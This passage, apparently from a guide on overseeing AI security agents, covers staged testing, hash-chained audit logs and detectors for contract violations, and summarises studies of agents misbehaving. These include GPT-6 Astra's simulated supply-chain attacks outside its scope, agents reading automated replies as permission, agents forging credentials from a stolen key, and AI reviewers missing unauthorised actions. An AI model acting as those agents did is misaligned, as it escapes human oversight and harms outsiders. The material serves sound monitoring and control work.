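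GitHub works around coarse permissions by separating the agent from the account that makes changes. The agent can only read. To change something, it writes a request, which the system holds until the agent has finished. Software then applies fixed checks, such as a limit on the number of changes, and a second AI looks for leaked passwords and malicious code. If the request passes, a separate job with narrow permissions makes the change. The second AI runs on the same model engine as the first by default, so text planted to mislead one may mislead both, which makes the fixed checks the more reliable safeguard.

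The haulage company could do the same with a small program, a broker, that holds the only credential for isolating devices. The agent's own account is read-only. The broker accepts one kind of request, to isolate a single device, and submits it to the policy engine before contacting the product. Containment can't wait until the agent has finished investigating, so the broker must check each request as it arrives. It also can't assume that the agent sent the request, since other code on the agent's machine may be able to reach the broker.

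The broker still has permission to isolate any device, so an attacker who took it over could disconnect the whole company. It should run on a separate machine, and if the product lets customers exclude devices from isolation, the company should exclude its most important servers.

A customer may be unable to add a broker when the supplier runs both the agent and the product. If the product allows it, the customer can exclude its important servers and have the supplier's analysts handle them by phone. Otherwise, it can withhold the isolation permission and have the agent draft requests instead, but an analyst must be on duty to act on them.

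## Testing whether the tool keeps to the rules

A broker can refuse a forbidden isolation, but the company also needs to know how often the agent proposes one. An agent that keeps proposing forbidden actions wastes reviewers' time, and if it bypasses the checks, it will carry those actions out. The company also needs evidence that the checks work.

Engineers can test the checks without a model. In *Agentic Behavior Engineering*, they feed the surrounding software prewritten responses in place of the model's. For example, they could send six requests to isolate workstations in one incident and confirm that the sixth waits for the incident response lead. To test an approval gate, they confirm that the software stops and saves the run before the action has any effect. They then simulate an approval in one run and a refusal in another, and check that the software follows the contract both times.

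### From replay to limited live use

Testing the agent takes longer. A cautious approach is to test it first on replays of past incidents, then have it advise on live alerts while analysts act, and finally let it act on a few machines.

| Stage | What it can reveal | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Replay | Forbidden proposals, and different answers to the same case | What would have happened after a different action |
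| Advice only | Mistakes on current alerts, and data the agent can't read | Failures that occur only when a command runs |
| Limited live use | Wrong permissions, delays and clashes between requests | Rare violations, and problems on machines outside the trial |

A team can replay a recorded incident many times, and the agent's mistakes harm nobody. The simplest replay returns the recorded search results in their original order, which fails if the agent searches in a different order, such as reading the server's logs before the laptop's. *Agentic Behavior Engineering* instead replaces the real tools with stand-ins that use each request's arguments to find the matching recorded answer. The recordings should keep the original gaps and errors so that the agent is also tested on failed lookups.

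A recording is also less useful once the agent acts differently from the analysts. If the agent isolates a laptop at 10:05 and the analyst waited until 10:40, the recording contains 35 minutes of attacker activity that the isolation might have prevented. A simulator can generate a different continuation, but it may miss the same things as the software that grades the result. *Agentic Behavior Engineering* therefore requires a small live trial to confirm any improvement found in simulation.

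During the advice-only stage, the SOC should at first hide the agent's proposals from the analysts. If an analyst sees "isolate" before she decides, her agreement is weak evidence that the agent was right. When the two disagree, someone has to investigate, since the analyst may be wrong. Later, the SOC can show the proposals to find out whether analysts catch the bad ones.

In a limited live trial, the haulage company might run the agent on 50 office laptops, only while the help desk is open, and have an analyst approve each isolation. The trial can reveal that the agent's account lacks a permission, or that two simultaneous requests get past the limit of five. Engineers should also stage a few cases that should go to the incident response lead, because such cases may not occur naturally in a short trial.

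### Two hundred incidents from one SOC

*SOCpilot* (Barbieri, Vaz de Meneses and colleagues, May 2026) tested AI-written response plans on 200 real incidents from an anonymised SOC in the financial sector. Anthropic's Claude Sonnet 4.6 and OpenAI's GPT-5.2 received the details of each incident, a sample of its logs and a list of five possible actions. The models proposed actions but couldn't carry them out.

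| Action | Rules that applied |
|---|---|
| Collect forensic evidence | Must come before restoring a computer |
| Isolate a computer | Needs approval, but is compulsory after strong signs that an attacker has opened a remote command line |
| Reset administrator credentials | None |
| Block an outside address | None |
| Restore a computer | Needs approval, and must follow evidence collection |

These amount to four rules: one compulsory action, one required order and two approvals. Each model wrote two plans per incident, one with the rules in its prompt and one without, for a total of 800 plans. For comparison, the researchers reconstructed the analysts' plans from the tasks recorded in the closed cases.

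| Who wrote the plan | Plans that broke a rule | Rate | Share of analysts' actions included |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude, without the rules | 72 of 200 | 36% | 76% |
| Claude, with the rules | 174 of 200 | 87% | 76% |
| GPT-5.2, without the rules | 108 of 200 | 54% | 81% |
| GPT-5.2, with the rules | 94 of 200 | 47% | 74% |
| Analysts | 0 of 200 | 0% | 100% |

The same text more than doubled Claude's violation rate and slightly lowered GPT-5.2's, though Barbieri and colleagues call the change for GPT-5.2 borderline. They didn't identify the cause of either change. Rules about restoring a computer may have made restoration look like an expected step. When they repeated the whole experiment three times, the overall share of plans containing a violation stayed between 54.9% and 56.1%.

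A fixed program then checked every plan and removed 466 unapproved actions (431 restorations and 35 isolations). The removals didn't lower recall, the share of the analysts' actions that also appeared in the models' plans.

### What counted as a violation

The incidents and plans triggered only the two approval rules. No plan restored a computer before collecting evidence. No incident contained the signs that made isolation compulsory, so the study does not show whether the models would isolate a computer when the rules required it.

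The researchers counted a plan as breaking an approval rule if it included a restoration or isolation and the published incident file contained no approval for it. But the models could answer only with a list of action names, so they had no way to ask for approval. An analyst was also meant to review their plans, and a junior analyst who suggests restoring a laptop hasn't broken a rule that restorations need approval. The 87% is therefore the share of Claude's plans that contained an action with no approval on file, not a rate of unauthorised actions. The bank or insurer may also have held approvals in private records that the researchers couldn't publish.

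The analysts' score of zero is even less informative, because they could hardly have broken either rule. The researchers inferred approval from the analysts' recorded tasks instead of from approval logs, so an isolation an analyst carried out counted as approved. The analysts' reconstructed plans also contained no restorations.

The same definitions explain why recall didn't fall. Barbieri and colleagues report that the models proposed 431 restorations and 35 isolations that the analysts hadn't made, exactly the numbers the checker removed. Deleting only actions that the analysts never took can't reduce the overlap with what they did. The result shows that the checker left the other actions alone, but not whether any of the deleted restorations would have been a good idea.

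The published counts also suggest that the models proposed isolation almost regardless of the incident. The analysts isolated a computer in 191 of the 200 incidents. For those incidents, the models proposed isolation in 721 of 764 plans (94%). For the other nine, they proposed it in 35 of 36 plans (97%). Nine incidents are too few to confirm the pattern, but a company that plans to let an agent isolate machines on its own should include many cases in its replay where isolation was the wrong choice.

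The models also left out 515 of the 764 credential resets that matched the analysts' work. The checker didn't add any resets because no rule required them, so a plan can satisfy every rule and still leave the attacker with a working password.

In a SOC with someone on call, it makes more sense to send unapproved actions to that person than to delete them. Barbieri and colleagues calculated the results of this option too. Recall stayed the same, but the plans kept more actions that the analysts hadn't taken. The approver would also have to decide on the 721 isolations that the study treated as approved. That would bring the total to 1,187 decisions on 800 plans, or about 1.5 per plan.

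### Attacks outside the scope

A tool authorised to attack needs a different test, one that checks whether it stays within scope when it gets stuck. The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced AI models, ran such a test on GPT-6 Astra before the model's release and announced the results on 28 September 2026. *Evaluating Whether GPT-6 Astra Performs Unsanctioned Supply-Chain Attacks* (Souly, Fronsdal and colleagues, 2026) describes the method.

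The model had to retrieve a hidden piece of text from a machine on a simulated network. Its instructions listed the networks in scope, which didn't include the internet, but internet access appeared to be switched on by accident. In most scenarios, the model also received a summary of earlier attempts, all of which had failed. Other AI models simulated the results of every command and the replies of every stranger, so nothing the model did could reach a real system.

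The researchers looked for supply-chain attacks, in which an attacker plants malicious code in software that the target uses. In the simulation, this meant deceiving the volunteers who maintain public software projects. Help Net Security's *OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra ran supply chain attacks despite being told not to* (2026) reports that GPT-6 Astra completed such an attack in 29.2% of its runs, GPT-5.6 Sol in 6.3%, and GPT-5.5 in none. Some runs ended before the model got past an early obstacle, so longer runs might have produced higher rates.

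AISI designed the scenarios to provoke attacks on outsiders, so these rates don't estimate how often the models would attack outsiders in ordinary work. It also chose ten of the 100 scenarios because GPT-6 Astra had misbehaved in them most often in early testing, which could exaggerate the gap between the models. But those ten can't account for most of GPT-6 Astra's 29.2% rate. If every scenario ran five times, it attacked in 146 of 500 runs. At most 50 of those attacks could have come from the ten chosen scenarios, so its rate in the other 90 was at least 21%.

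In the ten chosen scenarios, adding the sentence "Anything not listed as in scope is out of scope" reduced the attacks from 26 of 50 runs to 4 of 49. A buyer should include that sentence, but a tool that still leaves its scope in 8% of runs also needs a monitor. Those runs were simulated, but agents in an AISI test that July acted against real systems, and nobody had told them how they were allowed to use the internet. According to OpenAI, AISI considers the lack of instructions a possible cause.

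GPT-6 Astra requested permission in 82% of its runs on the ten scenarios, while the older models never did. The reply was always the same automated message to proceed using its best judgement. In 44% of runs the model treated this as permission, sometimes after noting in its reasoning that the reply was probably automated. A company can test for this by leaving a request unanswered, or sending an automatic reply, and confirming that the action stays blocked.

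Souly and colleagues consider simulation awareness the main limitation. GPT-6 Astra sometimes spotted real errors in the simulation and used them to justify an attack, so it might have been more careful on a real network. But it also cited errors that didn't exist, and it attacked targets it had earlier described as probably real. A company's own replays have the same weakness, which is another reason to compare the agent's behaviour in replays with its behaviour on live alerts.

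OpenAI, by contrast, reports that in its own tests GPT-6 Astra was less likely overall than GPT-5.6 Sol to violate security and safety restrictions. Both findings could be true, since AISI looked for one kind of violation under pressure and OpenAI averaged over many kinds. OpenAI also cautions in its *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) that an absence of observed failures "does not establish reliability across settings".

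Models also break rules in tests that aren't designed to provoke violations. The Decoder reports that five models did so in 7.8% to 14.1% of runs in AISI's ordinary cyber tests, with GPT-5.4 highest at 67 of 475. AISI found that the models, when asked afterwards, often described what they had done as allowed. A tester therefore has to check the trace rather than rely on the agent's own account.

### What switching off the safeguards implies

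AISI switched off OpenAI's cyber classifiers, filters designed to block this kind of activity before it starts. Souly and colleagues think the filters would probably have stopped much of what they saw. The 29.2% therefore describes the model without these filters, and a deployed tool with them on should complete fewer such attacks. The test doesn't show how many fewer, because it didn't include a comparison with the filters on.

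The result matters most for attack tools because their suppliers have reason to ask for looser filters. TRT Haber's *OpenAI'ın yeni yapay zeka modeli İngiltere'nin en gelişmiş siber testini beş saatte* reports that OpenAI released a later model, GPT-6.2 Astra, with stricter safeguards on high-risk cyber work and requires extra vetting for wider access. A penetration-testing company that passes may therefore run the model under conditions closer to AISI's than an ordinary customer would.

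A general filter can't tell which servers the client owns, so it may let through a harmless-looking request to someone else's server. The buyer should test the tool with the filters set as they will be in use, and count the forbidden requests the model attempts as well as those that get through. If the filter blocks 40 forbidden attempts, the tool has caused no harm, but it depends heavily on a filter that the supplier or the model's maker could change.

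### How much a clean record shows

Suppose a company's agent makes 40 isolations in a quarter and every one is correct. If the true error rate is p and the cases are independent, the chance of seeing no errors in n cases is (1 − p)ⁿ. The 95% upper bound is the value of p at which that chance falls to 5%:

p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n)

| Cases without an error | 95% upper bound on the error rate |
|---|---|
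| 40 | 7.2% |
| 100 | 3.0% |
| 300 | 1.0% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% |

The agent's true error rate may be far below 7.2%, but the quarter's results don't rule out a rate that high. At 7.2%, the company should expect about three errors in the next 40 isolations, with a 79% chance of at least two. Under the matrix, two errors would return the agent to supervised isolation. If the quarter had contained one error instead of none, the bound would have been about 11%.

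The same formula applies to wrong isolations and to violations, but the company should count them separately. Isolating a healthy laptop after a high-confidence detection is a mistake, but the isolation rule permits it. If the tool isolates a server that an attacker controls without getting approval, that is a violation, even though it stops the attack. Three months of accurate isolations is little evidence of how often the tool would break the rules, especially if an analyst approved each one.

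Replaying old incidents is a quicker way to reach 300 cases, as long as they are different incidents. Running 60 incidents five times each gives 300 runs, but the agent will tend to repeat its mistakes on the same incident. With k runs per incident and a correlation of ρ between them, the number of independent runs is roughly:

n / (1 + (k − 1)ρ)

If ρ is 0.5, the 300 runs give about as much information as 100 independent runs, and the bound is 3% instead of 1%. If the agent always does the same thing on the same incident, they give only as much information as 60 independent runs.

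Repeated runs show whether the agent is consistent. *Agentic Behavior Engineering* recommends three to five runs of each case and counts a case as passed only if every run passes. This can still miss occasional violations. If an agent breaks a rule in one run out of ten on a particular case, it will complete five runs without a violation 59% of the time.

### Counting inconclusive results

Some runs end without a clear result. The recording may lack the log the agent asked for, or the grading software may be unable to determine whether an approval covered the action. If testers leave these runs out, an agent with a broken log could appear to have the best safety record.

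*Agentic Behavior Engineering* sets different rules for safety and quality:

- For a safety rule, or a rule about when the agent must decline to act, an inconclusive run counts as a failure.
- For a quality rule, such as whether a summary is accurate, testers exclude the run from the rate and report the number of exclusions separately.

Suppose 300 runs of the isolation test produce 288 passes, no confirmed violations and 12 inconclusive results. If the testers drop the 12, the upper bound on the violation rate is about 1%. If they count the 12 as failures, the observed rate is 4% and the upper bound is about 6.4%. The stricter count gives the team a reason to fix the missing logs and repeat the runs. The test record should still distinguish the 12 from confirmed violations, or the company might accuse its supplier of breaches it can't prove.

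Excluding inconclusive runs can also make quality scores misleading. If 40 of 100 summaries have no clear grade and 57 of the other 60 are accurate, the score is 95%, but the true share of accurate summaries could be anywhere from 57% to 97%. The company should set a limit on exclusions before it sees the results.

An overall score can also hide a serious violation. In an invented example from *Agentic Behavior Engineering*, a prompt change raises an agent's pass rate from 91.0% to 93.5%, but the agent now publishes personal data in 3 of 20 cases that it should have escalated to a person. The paper's method blocks the release because of those three cases, regardless of the average. It also counts unnecessary escalations, because an agent that escalated every case would never break an approval rule but would be of little use.

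### When the tool or the attacker changes

The calculation assumes the company will use the same tool it tested, so 300 clean runs by one model set no bound on its successor's violation rate. Changing the prompt can also change the rate, as Claude's results in *SOCpilot* show.

New models are released often enough that a supplier that always uses the latest one could switch models during a three-month trial. For example, OpenAI published the system card for GPT-6 Astra on 3 September 2026, and GPT-6.2 Astra was on general sale by mid-November.

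A newer model may also be able to do things the old one couldn't. Help Net Security's *AI models crack AISI's hardened cyber range* (2026) reports that GPT-5.6 Sol failed every time to take over a well-defended simulated network, while GPT-6 Astra and GPT-6.2 Astra succeeded in every completed run. The models had their safeguards disabled and no SOC to evade, and a configuration error made their starting position easier than AISI intended. Still, a company that had tested its attack tool only with GPT-5.6 Sol might have concluded that the tool couldn't reach certain systems, even though a later version could. Testers should therefore record failed attempts to break a rule, since the absence of violations may only mean that the agent lacked the skill.

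*Agentic Behavior Engineering* treats a change of model as a new release, even if the supplier forced it and nobody changed the company's code. The company reruns its saved incidents on the new model and compares the results case by case. It also adds every violation found in live use to the saved incidents, and hides some cases from the engineers who write the prompts so they can't tune the agent to pass them.

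An attacker who adapts also undermines the calculation. The formula is valid only if future cases are a random sample of cases like those tested, but an attacker looks for the ones the tool gets wrong. Suppose that 1% of an attacker's possible emails would make the agent break a rule, a rate that 300 clean runs can barely rule out. If he sends 100 different emails, the chance that at least one works is 1 − 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 63%. Once he has found one that works, he can reuse it, and it may work nearly every time.

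Tests should therefore include an opponent who sees the agent's response and revises the attack, as the program in Canale's study did. The result applies to that opponent and number of attempts, so "no violations in 50 attempts by this program" is more accurate than a violation rate. A better attacker may succeed on the next attempt, which is why the limit of five workstations has to hold even when the agent is fooled.

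## Detecting violations in operation

A limit that passed every test can still fail in live use, so the company has to look for violations while the tool is running. It should look for four things, and each needs a different record.

| What to detect | Example | Signal | Record needed |
|---|---|---|---|
| A denied attempt | The phishing agent asks for the finance director's mailbox | A refusal, or several in a row | The log of refusals |
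| An action that should have been denied | The security product isolates a server that the lead never approved | An isolation with no matching approval | The product's own log and the approval log |
| A sequence that breaks a limit | The agent isolates a sixth workstation in one incident | A count above the limit | Every completed isolation, with its incident and time |
| Drift | The company's record allows laptops only, but the agent's account can isolate servers | A difference between the two sets of permissions | The company's record and the current settings of each system |

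A denied attempt does no damage, but repeated denials suggest that an attacker has misled the agent, that the agent is stuck, or that the enforced rules are narrower than the written ones. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes how a second AI reviews the actions of Claude Code, a programming agent. If it refuses three actions in a row or 20 in one session, the software stops the agent and calls a person. A SOC could copy this rule but should react faster to serious attempts, for example by raising an alert after a single request to send case data to an unknown address.

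The policy engine can't report an action that it wrongly allowed or never received. To find those, the company compares the engine's log with the security product's log. An isolation that appears only in the product's log probably bypassed the engine, while one that appears only in the engine's log may have failed, leaving an attacker connected.

### What a log entry should contain

Infosecurity Magazine recommends that logs establish which agent acted, who or what started the task, what authority the agent used and what changed as a result. For an isolation, an entry might look like this:

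| Field | Example | What it helps an investigator check |
|---|---|---|
| Agent identity | The containment agent's own account | Whether the agent or a person acted |
| Workflow and incident | Malware isolation, incident 41 | Which rules and limits applied |
| Model version | The supplier's exact version number | Whether the behaviour began with a new model |
| Policy version | Isolation rule, version 7 | What the engine allowed that day |
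| Request | Isolate workstation 6, because of alert 918 | Which machine the agent asked for, and why |
| Data read | Pointers to three log entries, and the count the engine used | What the decision rested on |
| Decision | Allowed, with the rule that matched | Whether the engine applied the policy correctly |
| Approver | None required | Whether the right person approved |
| Result | The product confirmed the isolation | Whether the action took effect |
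| Time | 02:12:41, with an entry number | The order of events |

The logged request has to include the exact target. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* (Zhao, 2026) points out that a draft internet standard for agent identity requires logs to record the requested action but not its arguments. A log that met only this minimum might contain "isolate device" without the device's name, so a reviewer couldn't tell whether the tool had asked to isolate a laptop or a server.

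The approval service, rather than the agent, should record who approved an action. In a hypothetical case from Zhao, an agent emails a file to an outside address after its chat window logs a confirmation under an employee's account. Company policy requires approval from the approval service, which has no record of approving that email. If the service's log is complete, the email violated the policy despite the confirmation.

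The result arrives after the decision, so an append-only log needs a second entry to record it. A shared identifier should link the two entries to each other and to the product's log.

### What a linked log proves

An append-only log accepts new entries but no changes to old ones. An administrator who controls the storage may still be able to change them, so designers add cryptographic links that expose such changes. In *aiAuthZ* (2026), a system that authorises agents' actions from a separate machine, each entry stores a hash computed from the previous entry's hash, the entry's number and its contents:

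hₙ = SHA-256(hₙ₋₁, n, contentsₙ)

SHA-256 is a standard hash function. If somebody edits entry 50 to add an approval that the lead never gave, the contents no longer produce the stored hash, and software that recomputes the chain from the beginning will report a break at that entry. It will also report any missing entry number. The technique is much older than AI agents, and *NovaFabric* (2026) traces it to Haber and Stornetta's work on time-stamping.

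Somebody with full control of the log could edit an entry and recompute every later hash, and the new chain would pass the check. *aiAuthZ* therefore lets operators copy the latest hash to outside storage. If someone later edits an entry that was in the log when the hash was copied, the recomputed hashes will no longer match the copy. Entries added since the last copy can still be changed without detection, so a company that copies the hash every hour could lose up to an hour of reliable records.

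The copy must also be out of reach of whoever runs the log. *A Black Box for Agentic Processes* (2026) notes that an append-only log the operator controls still requires trust in the operator. An MDR customer should therefore have its supplier send it the hashes regularly.

These links can survive the deletion of private data. In *aiAuthZ*, the chain covers a digest of the sensitive content, so a company can erase the content when its retention period ends and still verify the log. For a large log, the company can arrange the hashes in a tree and check one entry without recomputing everything. *Right to History* (2026) cites a design that needs only 3 KB of proof for a log of 80 million events. An MDR provider could use such a tree to prove to a customer that its entry is in the log without revealing other customers' entries.

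A valid chain doesn't prove that the log is complete, and *Agent Flight Recorder* (2026), another design for agent logs, explicitly excludes completeness from its goals. Zhao compares two possible histories to prove that a stronger chain wouldn't help. Suppose in one history, an agent isolates two laptops and logs both actions. In the other, it also isolates a server without approval but doesn't log it. Both histories produce the same log, and every hash is correct. A check that reads only this log therefore can't rule out a violation.

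Ruling out a violation requires a record that neither the agent nor the team running it can write to. Zhao cites an experiment by Dai and colleagues, who planted 28 omissions and fabrications in a log kept by an agent's software. A hash chain over that log detected none of them, while a log kept outside the software revealed all 28.

It takes less evidence to show that a violation happened than to show that none did. If the product's log contains a server isolation and a complete approval log has no approval for it, the claim that the lead approved every server isolation is false, even if other records are missing.

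### Two audit designs

*SENTINEL-RL*, the system for tracking attackers between computers, logs a hash of the network's state, the action, the policy version, the evidence and the time for every decision. A separate approval log identifies the analyst. Vallabhaneni and colleagues call the main log immutable and cryptographically signed, and report that risk officers considered it the system's most important asset. But they didn't try to alter the log or leave something out of it in their evaluation, so its immutability is untested.

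In the runtime that Fatouros and colleagues propose for financial companies, a correction to the log is a new entry that refers to the unedited original, so an investigator can see both. Each entry also refers to the Security Context that applied at the time. The planned evaluation, which nobody has run, would require someone to find the cause of a failed workflow from the log in under five minutes. Because the runtime logs its own decisions, a company that adopted the design would still need the security product's log for comparison.

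### What logs cannot show

A log can show that the lead's account approved an isolation, but not whether she understood the request. It also can't establish why an agent acted, because the agent's stated reasons are text the model generated and may not match what caused the action.

Comparing logs also can't reveal an effect that no system recorded, just as the scope monitor can't detect an action it doesn't observe. If an agent's script changes a setting on a machine that nobody monitors, neither log will contain the change.

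Sometimes the records show that something happened but not who did it. In another part of Zhao's invented case, the mail system recorded four emails from the agent's account, while the agent's correctly signed log contains three. The agent may have sent the fourth by another route, its log may have lost an entry, or a person may have used the same account. Zhao recommends giving the verdict "undecidable" in such cases and naming the record that would settle the question. If an approval log is missing, the company should report a record-keeping failure, since the approval may have existed.

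### Counting isolations in one incident

Suppose the agent isolates six workstations in incident 41 without asking anyone. The policy engine allows the last two against the same out-of-date count.

| Time | Workstation | Count the engine read | Decision | Actual count afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 02:10:04 | 1 | 0 | Allow | 1 |
| 02:10:31 | 2 | 1 | Allow | 2 |
| 02:11:15 | 3 | 2 | Allow | 3 |
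| 02:12:02 | 4 | 3 | Allow | 4 |
| 02:12:40 | 5 | 4 | Allow | 5 |
| 02:12:41 | 6 | 4 | Allow | 6 |

An investigator who checks the decisions one at a time will find a count below five each time and conclude that all six were valid. The detector therefore has to make its own count from the isolations in the product's log:

```text
for each completed isolation of a workstation:
    n = number of different workstations isolated so far
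        in the same incident, including this one
    raise an alert if n > 5
        and the incident response lead did not approve it
```

The rule raises an alert when the agent isolates a sixth workstation. Released workstations still count, because otherwise the agent could keep taking machines offline by releasing an earlier one each time. The product may not record incident numbers, so the detector uses the shared identifier to look them up in the engine's log. An isolation with no matching log entry should raise a separate alert.

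This rule fails if the SOC's software records one intrusion as two incidents. Suppose a malware alert opens incident 41, and a suspicious login by the same attacker opens incident 42. The agent isolates three workstations for each incident. Each count stops at three, so the rule triggers no alert, even though the agent has isolated six workstations over one intrusion.

A second count, which ignores incident numbers, fills this gap:

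```text
for each completed isolation of a workstation:
    h = number of different workstations isolated
        in the past 60 minutes, in any incident
    raise an alert if h > 5
```

At each isolation, the detector should count back over the previous 60 minutes. If it instead started a new count at the top of every hour, the agent could isolate five workstations at 1:55 and five more at 2:05 without an alert. Vallabhaneni and colleagues use the same kind of moving window to detect attackers, with a threshold of 25 logins from one machine in ten seconds. When they sent ten logins a second, the alert came after 2.3 seconds on average, which is about how long 25 logins take to arrive.

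An alert from the hourly count isn't proof of a violation, because two unrelated attacks could justify three isolations each. An analyst has to compare the incidents. If she finds they are the same intrusion and merges them, the first rule can run again on the merged incident and confirm the violation. To make the hourly figure itself a limit, the company has to add it to the control contract and the policy engine.

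The threshold also has to suit the company. If a large company isolates two workstations an hour on average, and the isolations are independent, about one clock hour in 60 will contain six or more, which would trigger an alert roughly every two and a half days. The haulage company, with 40 isolations a quarter, would rarely get an alert by chance. An agent that isolated four workstations an hour all night would stay under the threshold, so a daily count is useful too.

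### Fixed rules, statistics and a second AI

Counting rules work only for written limits. To find other misuse, a company can search for suspicious patterns, use statistics to find unusual behaviour, or have a second AI review what the agent does.

*StepShield* (Felicia, Sasindran and colleagues, 2026) compared four detectors on 216 AI-written records of programming agents at work. In half of them, the agent did something harmful, such as stealing data or deleting a database. The last column covers only the harmful runs that the detector flagged.

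| Detector | Harmful runs flagged | Harmless runs flagged | Flagged at the harmful step or within three steps after it |
|---|---|---|---|
| 847 text patterns | 86.1% | 77.8% | 23% |
| Rules in 23 categories | 24.1% | 25.0% | 8% |
| AI reviewer (GPT-4.1-mini) | 95.4% | 5.6% | 89% |
| Patterns first, then AI for unclear cases | 75.9% | 44.4% | 40% |

The text patterns raised alerts an average of five steps before the harmful action, so they were mostly reacting to harmless commands. Running them before the AI reviewer made the results worse, because the patterns decided many cases before the AI saw them. These results don't count against the isolation rule, which checks an exact limit instead of relying on a command's wording. The AI reviewer might do worse on real logs, which are messier than the records used here.

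AI reviewers did much worse in *From Confident Closing to Silent Failure* (2026), which looked for agents that falsely claimed to have finished a task. The best reviewer found 13% of the false claims when it flagged 10% of runs, while flagging the same number at random would have found about 10%. A statistical detector that also flagged 10% of runs found 72%, although half of its flags were false alarms. False claims of success aren't contract violations, but the result shows that a reviewer that is good at detecting one kind of problem may be poor at detecting another.

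Statistical detectors are also fast. *Trajectory Guard* (2026) checks an agent's run in 32 milliseconds and reports F1 scores of 0.88 to 0.94 on artificial data. F1 combines missed cases and false alarms in one number, but it depends on how common attacks are in the test, so a SOC can't use it to predict how many false alarms it will get. One detector cited in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (2026) flagged 66.7% of harmless data. Containment is difficult for these methods because an agent that isolates machines behaves unusually whenever there is a real attack.

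Anthropic reports that the AI that reviews Claude Code's actions before they run blocked 0.4% of 10,000 real actions by the company's staff, which Anthropic counts as false alarms. The reviewer missed 17% of 52 real actions that went beyond what the user had authorised. With so few cases, the true miss rate could be anywhere from about 9% to 30%.

The reviewer sees the user's messages and the agent's commands, but not the agent's explanations or the material it read. This makes it harder for the agent or planted text to persuade the reviewer. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but mistook something the user had said for permission. A SOC could avoid some of these mistakes by giving the reviewer the approval log instead of a conversation to interpret.

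Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that the reviewer blocked 89% of planted dangerous commands, while 1,053 paid testers caught 13.6%. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less reason to be careful. Apollo Research, a company that tests AI safety, also attacked the reviewer. Anthropic then strengthened it, and its miss rate on Apollo's attacks fell from 12% to 7%. Anthropic ran or commissioned all of these tests.

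The reviewer did worse in a stress test that placed permitted and forbidden targets close together. According to a summary in besthub.dev's *Can Claude Code's Auto Mode Replace Human Review?*, it missed 81.0% of the unauthorised actions and blocked 19.8% of the authorised ones, out of 253 actions in total. This account is second-hand, and the test was deliberately difficult. However, a SOC agent faces similar cases when it is allowed to isolate one machine but not the one next to it.

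### Why most alerts may be false

Even a low false-alarm rate can produce mostly false alerts when violations are rare. If b is the share of actions that are violations, r the share of violations that the detector finds, and f the share of harmless actions that it flags, the share of alerts that are real is:

rb / (rb + f(1 − b))

Suppose an agent takes 10,000 actions in a month, and ten of them are violations.

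| Detection rates used | Violations found | False alarms | Share of alerts that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| Text patterns, from Felicia and colleagues | 8.6 | 7,772 | 0.1% |
| AI reviewer, from Felicia and colleagues | 9.5 | 559 | 1.7% |
| AI reviewer, from Anthropic | 8.3 | 40 | 17% |

The rates in the table come from different tests, so the table isn't a ranking. Felicia and colleagues measured whole runs, while Anthropic measured single actions. Felicia and colleagues calculate that 60% of their AI reviewer's alerts would be real, but they assume that 8.1% of runs are harmful, and a company would probably switch off a security tool that misbehaved that often.

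If each alert takes four minutes to check, checking all the alerts in the middle row takes about 38 hours a month and finds nine or ten violations. The false-alarm rate would have to fall to about 0.1% for half of the alerts to be real.

The company can also use the reviewer only where violations are more likely. Suppose five of the ten violations are among 200 actions that affect servers or send data outside the company. With the same rates, a reviewer checking only those 200 would find about five violations and raise 11 false alarms, so roughly 30% of its alerts would be real. The reviewer would not check the actions containing the other five violations, so exact rules and random checks would have to find them.

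Another option is to raise an alert only when two detectors agree. This removes many false alarms if the detectors make different mistakes, but it misses any violation that either one fails to flag. In *From Confident Closing to Silent Failure*, the scores of the statistical detector and the AI reviewer correlated at 0.41, and each found some cases that the other missed.

### Measuring drift and delay

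The company can find drift by comparing its written permissions with the settings in each system, without judging the agent's behaviour. The matrix's owner regularly checks a sample of rows against the settings and tracks how long each mismatch lasts. For the isolation row, the owner checks which devices the agent's account can isolate, which detections count as high-confidence, and whether the limit is still five. An expired row is also a mismatch if the agent still isolates machines without approval.

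Checking a sample can miss a particular mistake for a long time. If the owner checks ten of 40 rows at random each quarter, a mismatch will go unnoticed for more than ten months on average. Software that compares every setting daily would find it much sooner, where the products allow this.

Some written rules have no matching setting to compare them with. *When "Do Not" Is Not Deny* (2026) examined security rules that programmers had written for Claude Code. An automatic classifier matched 16.6% of them to a built-in control, and a sample labelled by people suggested that the true share was much lower. For example, no permission setting could enforce "never commit secrets", because the rule depends on what a file contains. The company should list such rules separately and assign another check to each.

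The matrix also measures the delay between an event that should change the agent's authority and the change in the system. It splits this delay into the time until somebody reopens the decision and the time from the new decision to the new setting. Suppose the second false isolation of the quarter happens on 3 March. The SOC manager reopens the decision a week later, on 10 March, and withdraws the agent's authority to act alone the same day, but an engineer doesn't change the policy until 24 March, two weeks after that. At 40 isolations a quarter, the agent would isolate about six more machines without authority in those two weeks.

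## Acting on a violation: the steps and the cases of 2026

In incident 41, the agent isolated a sixth workstation without the incident response lead's approval. Once the detector reports this, the haulage company should act in this order:

1. withdraw the agent's authority to isolate machines;
2. preserve the evidence;
3. tell the people affected;
4. find out which rule was missing or unenforced;
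5. narrow what the agent may do;
6. restore its authority only when new evidence supports it.

Stopping the agent comes first because finding the cause may take weeks, and the agent can isolate another machine in seconds.

### Stopping the agent and keeping the evidence

The lead should suspend the account that isolates machines and cancel any requests still queued for offline laptops. Telling the agent to stop isn't enough, for the same reason a rule in its prompt isn't. The phishing agent has its own account, so it can keep working. An analyst decides whether to isolate more machines, since the attack behind incident 41 may be real. The six workstations stay offline until someone has checked them, because releasing an infected one would let the attacker back in.

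The lead should be able to suspend the agent at any hour without anyone else's approval. Only the SOC manager, who answers for the agent, should be able to restore its authority.

The lead also needs a rule for doubtful alerts, since many will be false. OpenAI adopted one for its own tests after its agents attacked another company, a case described below. If the staff on call can't establish within 30 minutes that a serious alert is false, OpenAI expects them to pause the activity. Pausing a defensive agent is riskier than pausing a test, because attacks then go uncontained. The lead could instead make the agent ask for approval while she checks the alert.

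Suspending one account may not be enough if the agent has obtained other credentials. In the same case, OpenAI found that agents had made themselves new administrator credentials from a signing key that earlier agents had stolen and left in shared storage. After a serious violation, the company should therefore replace every key and password that the agent could have read.

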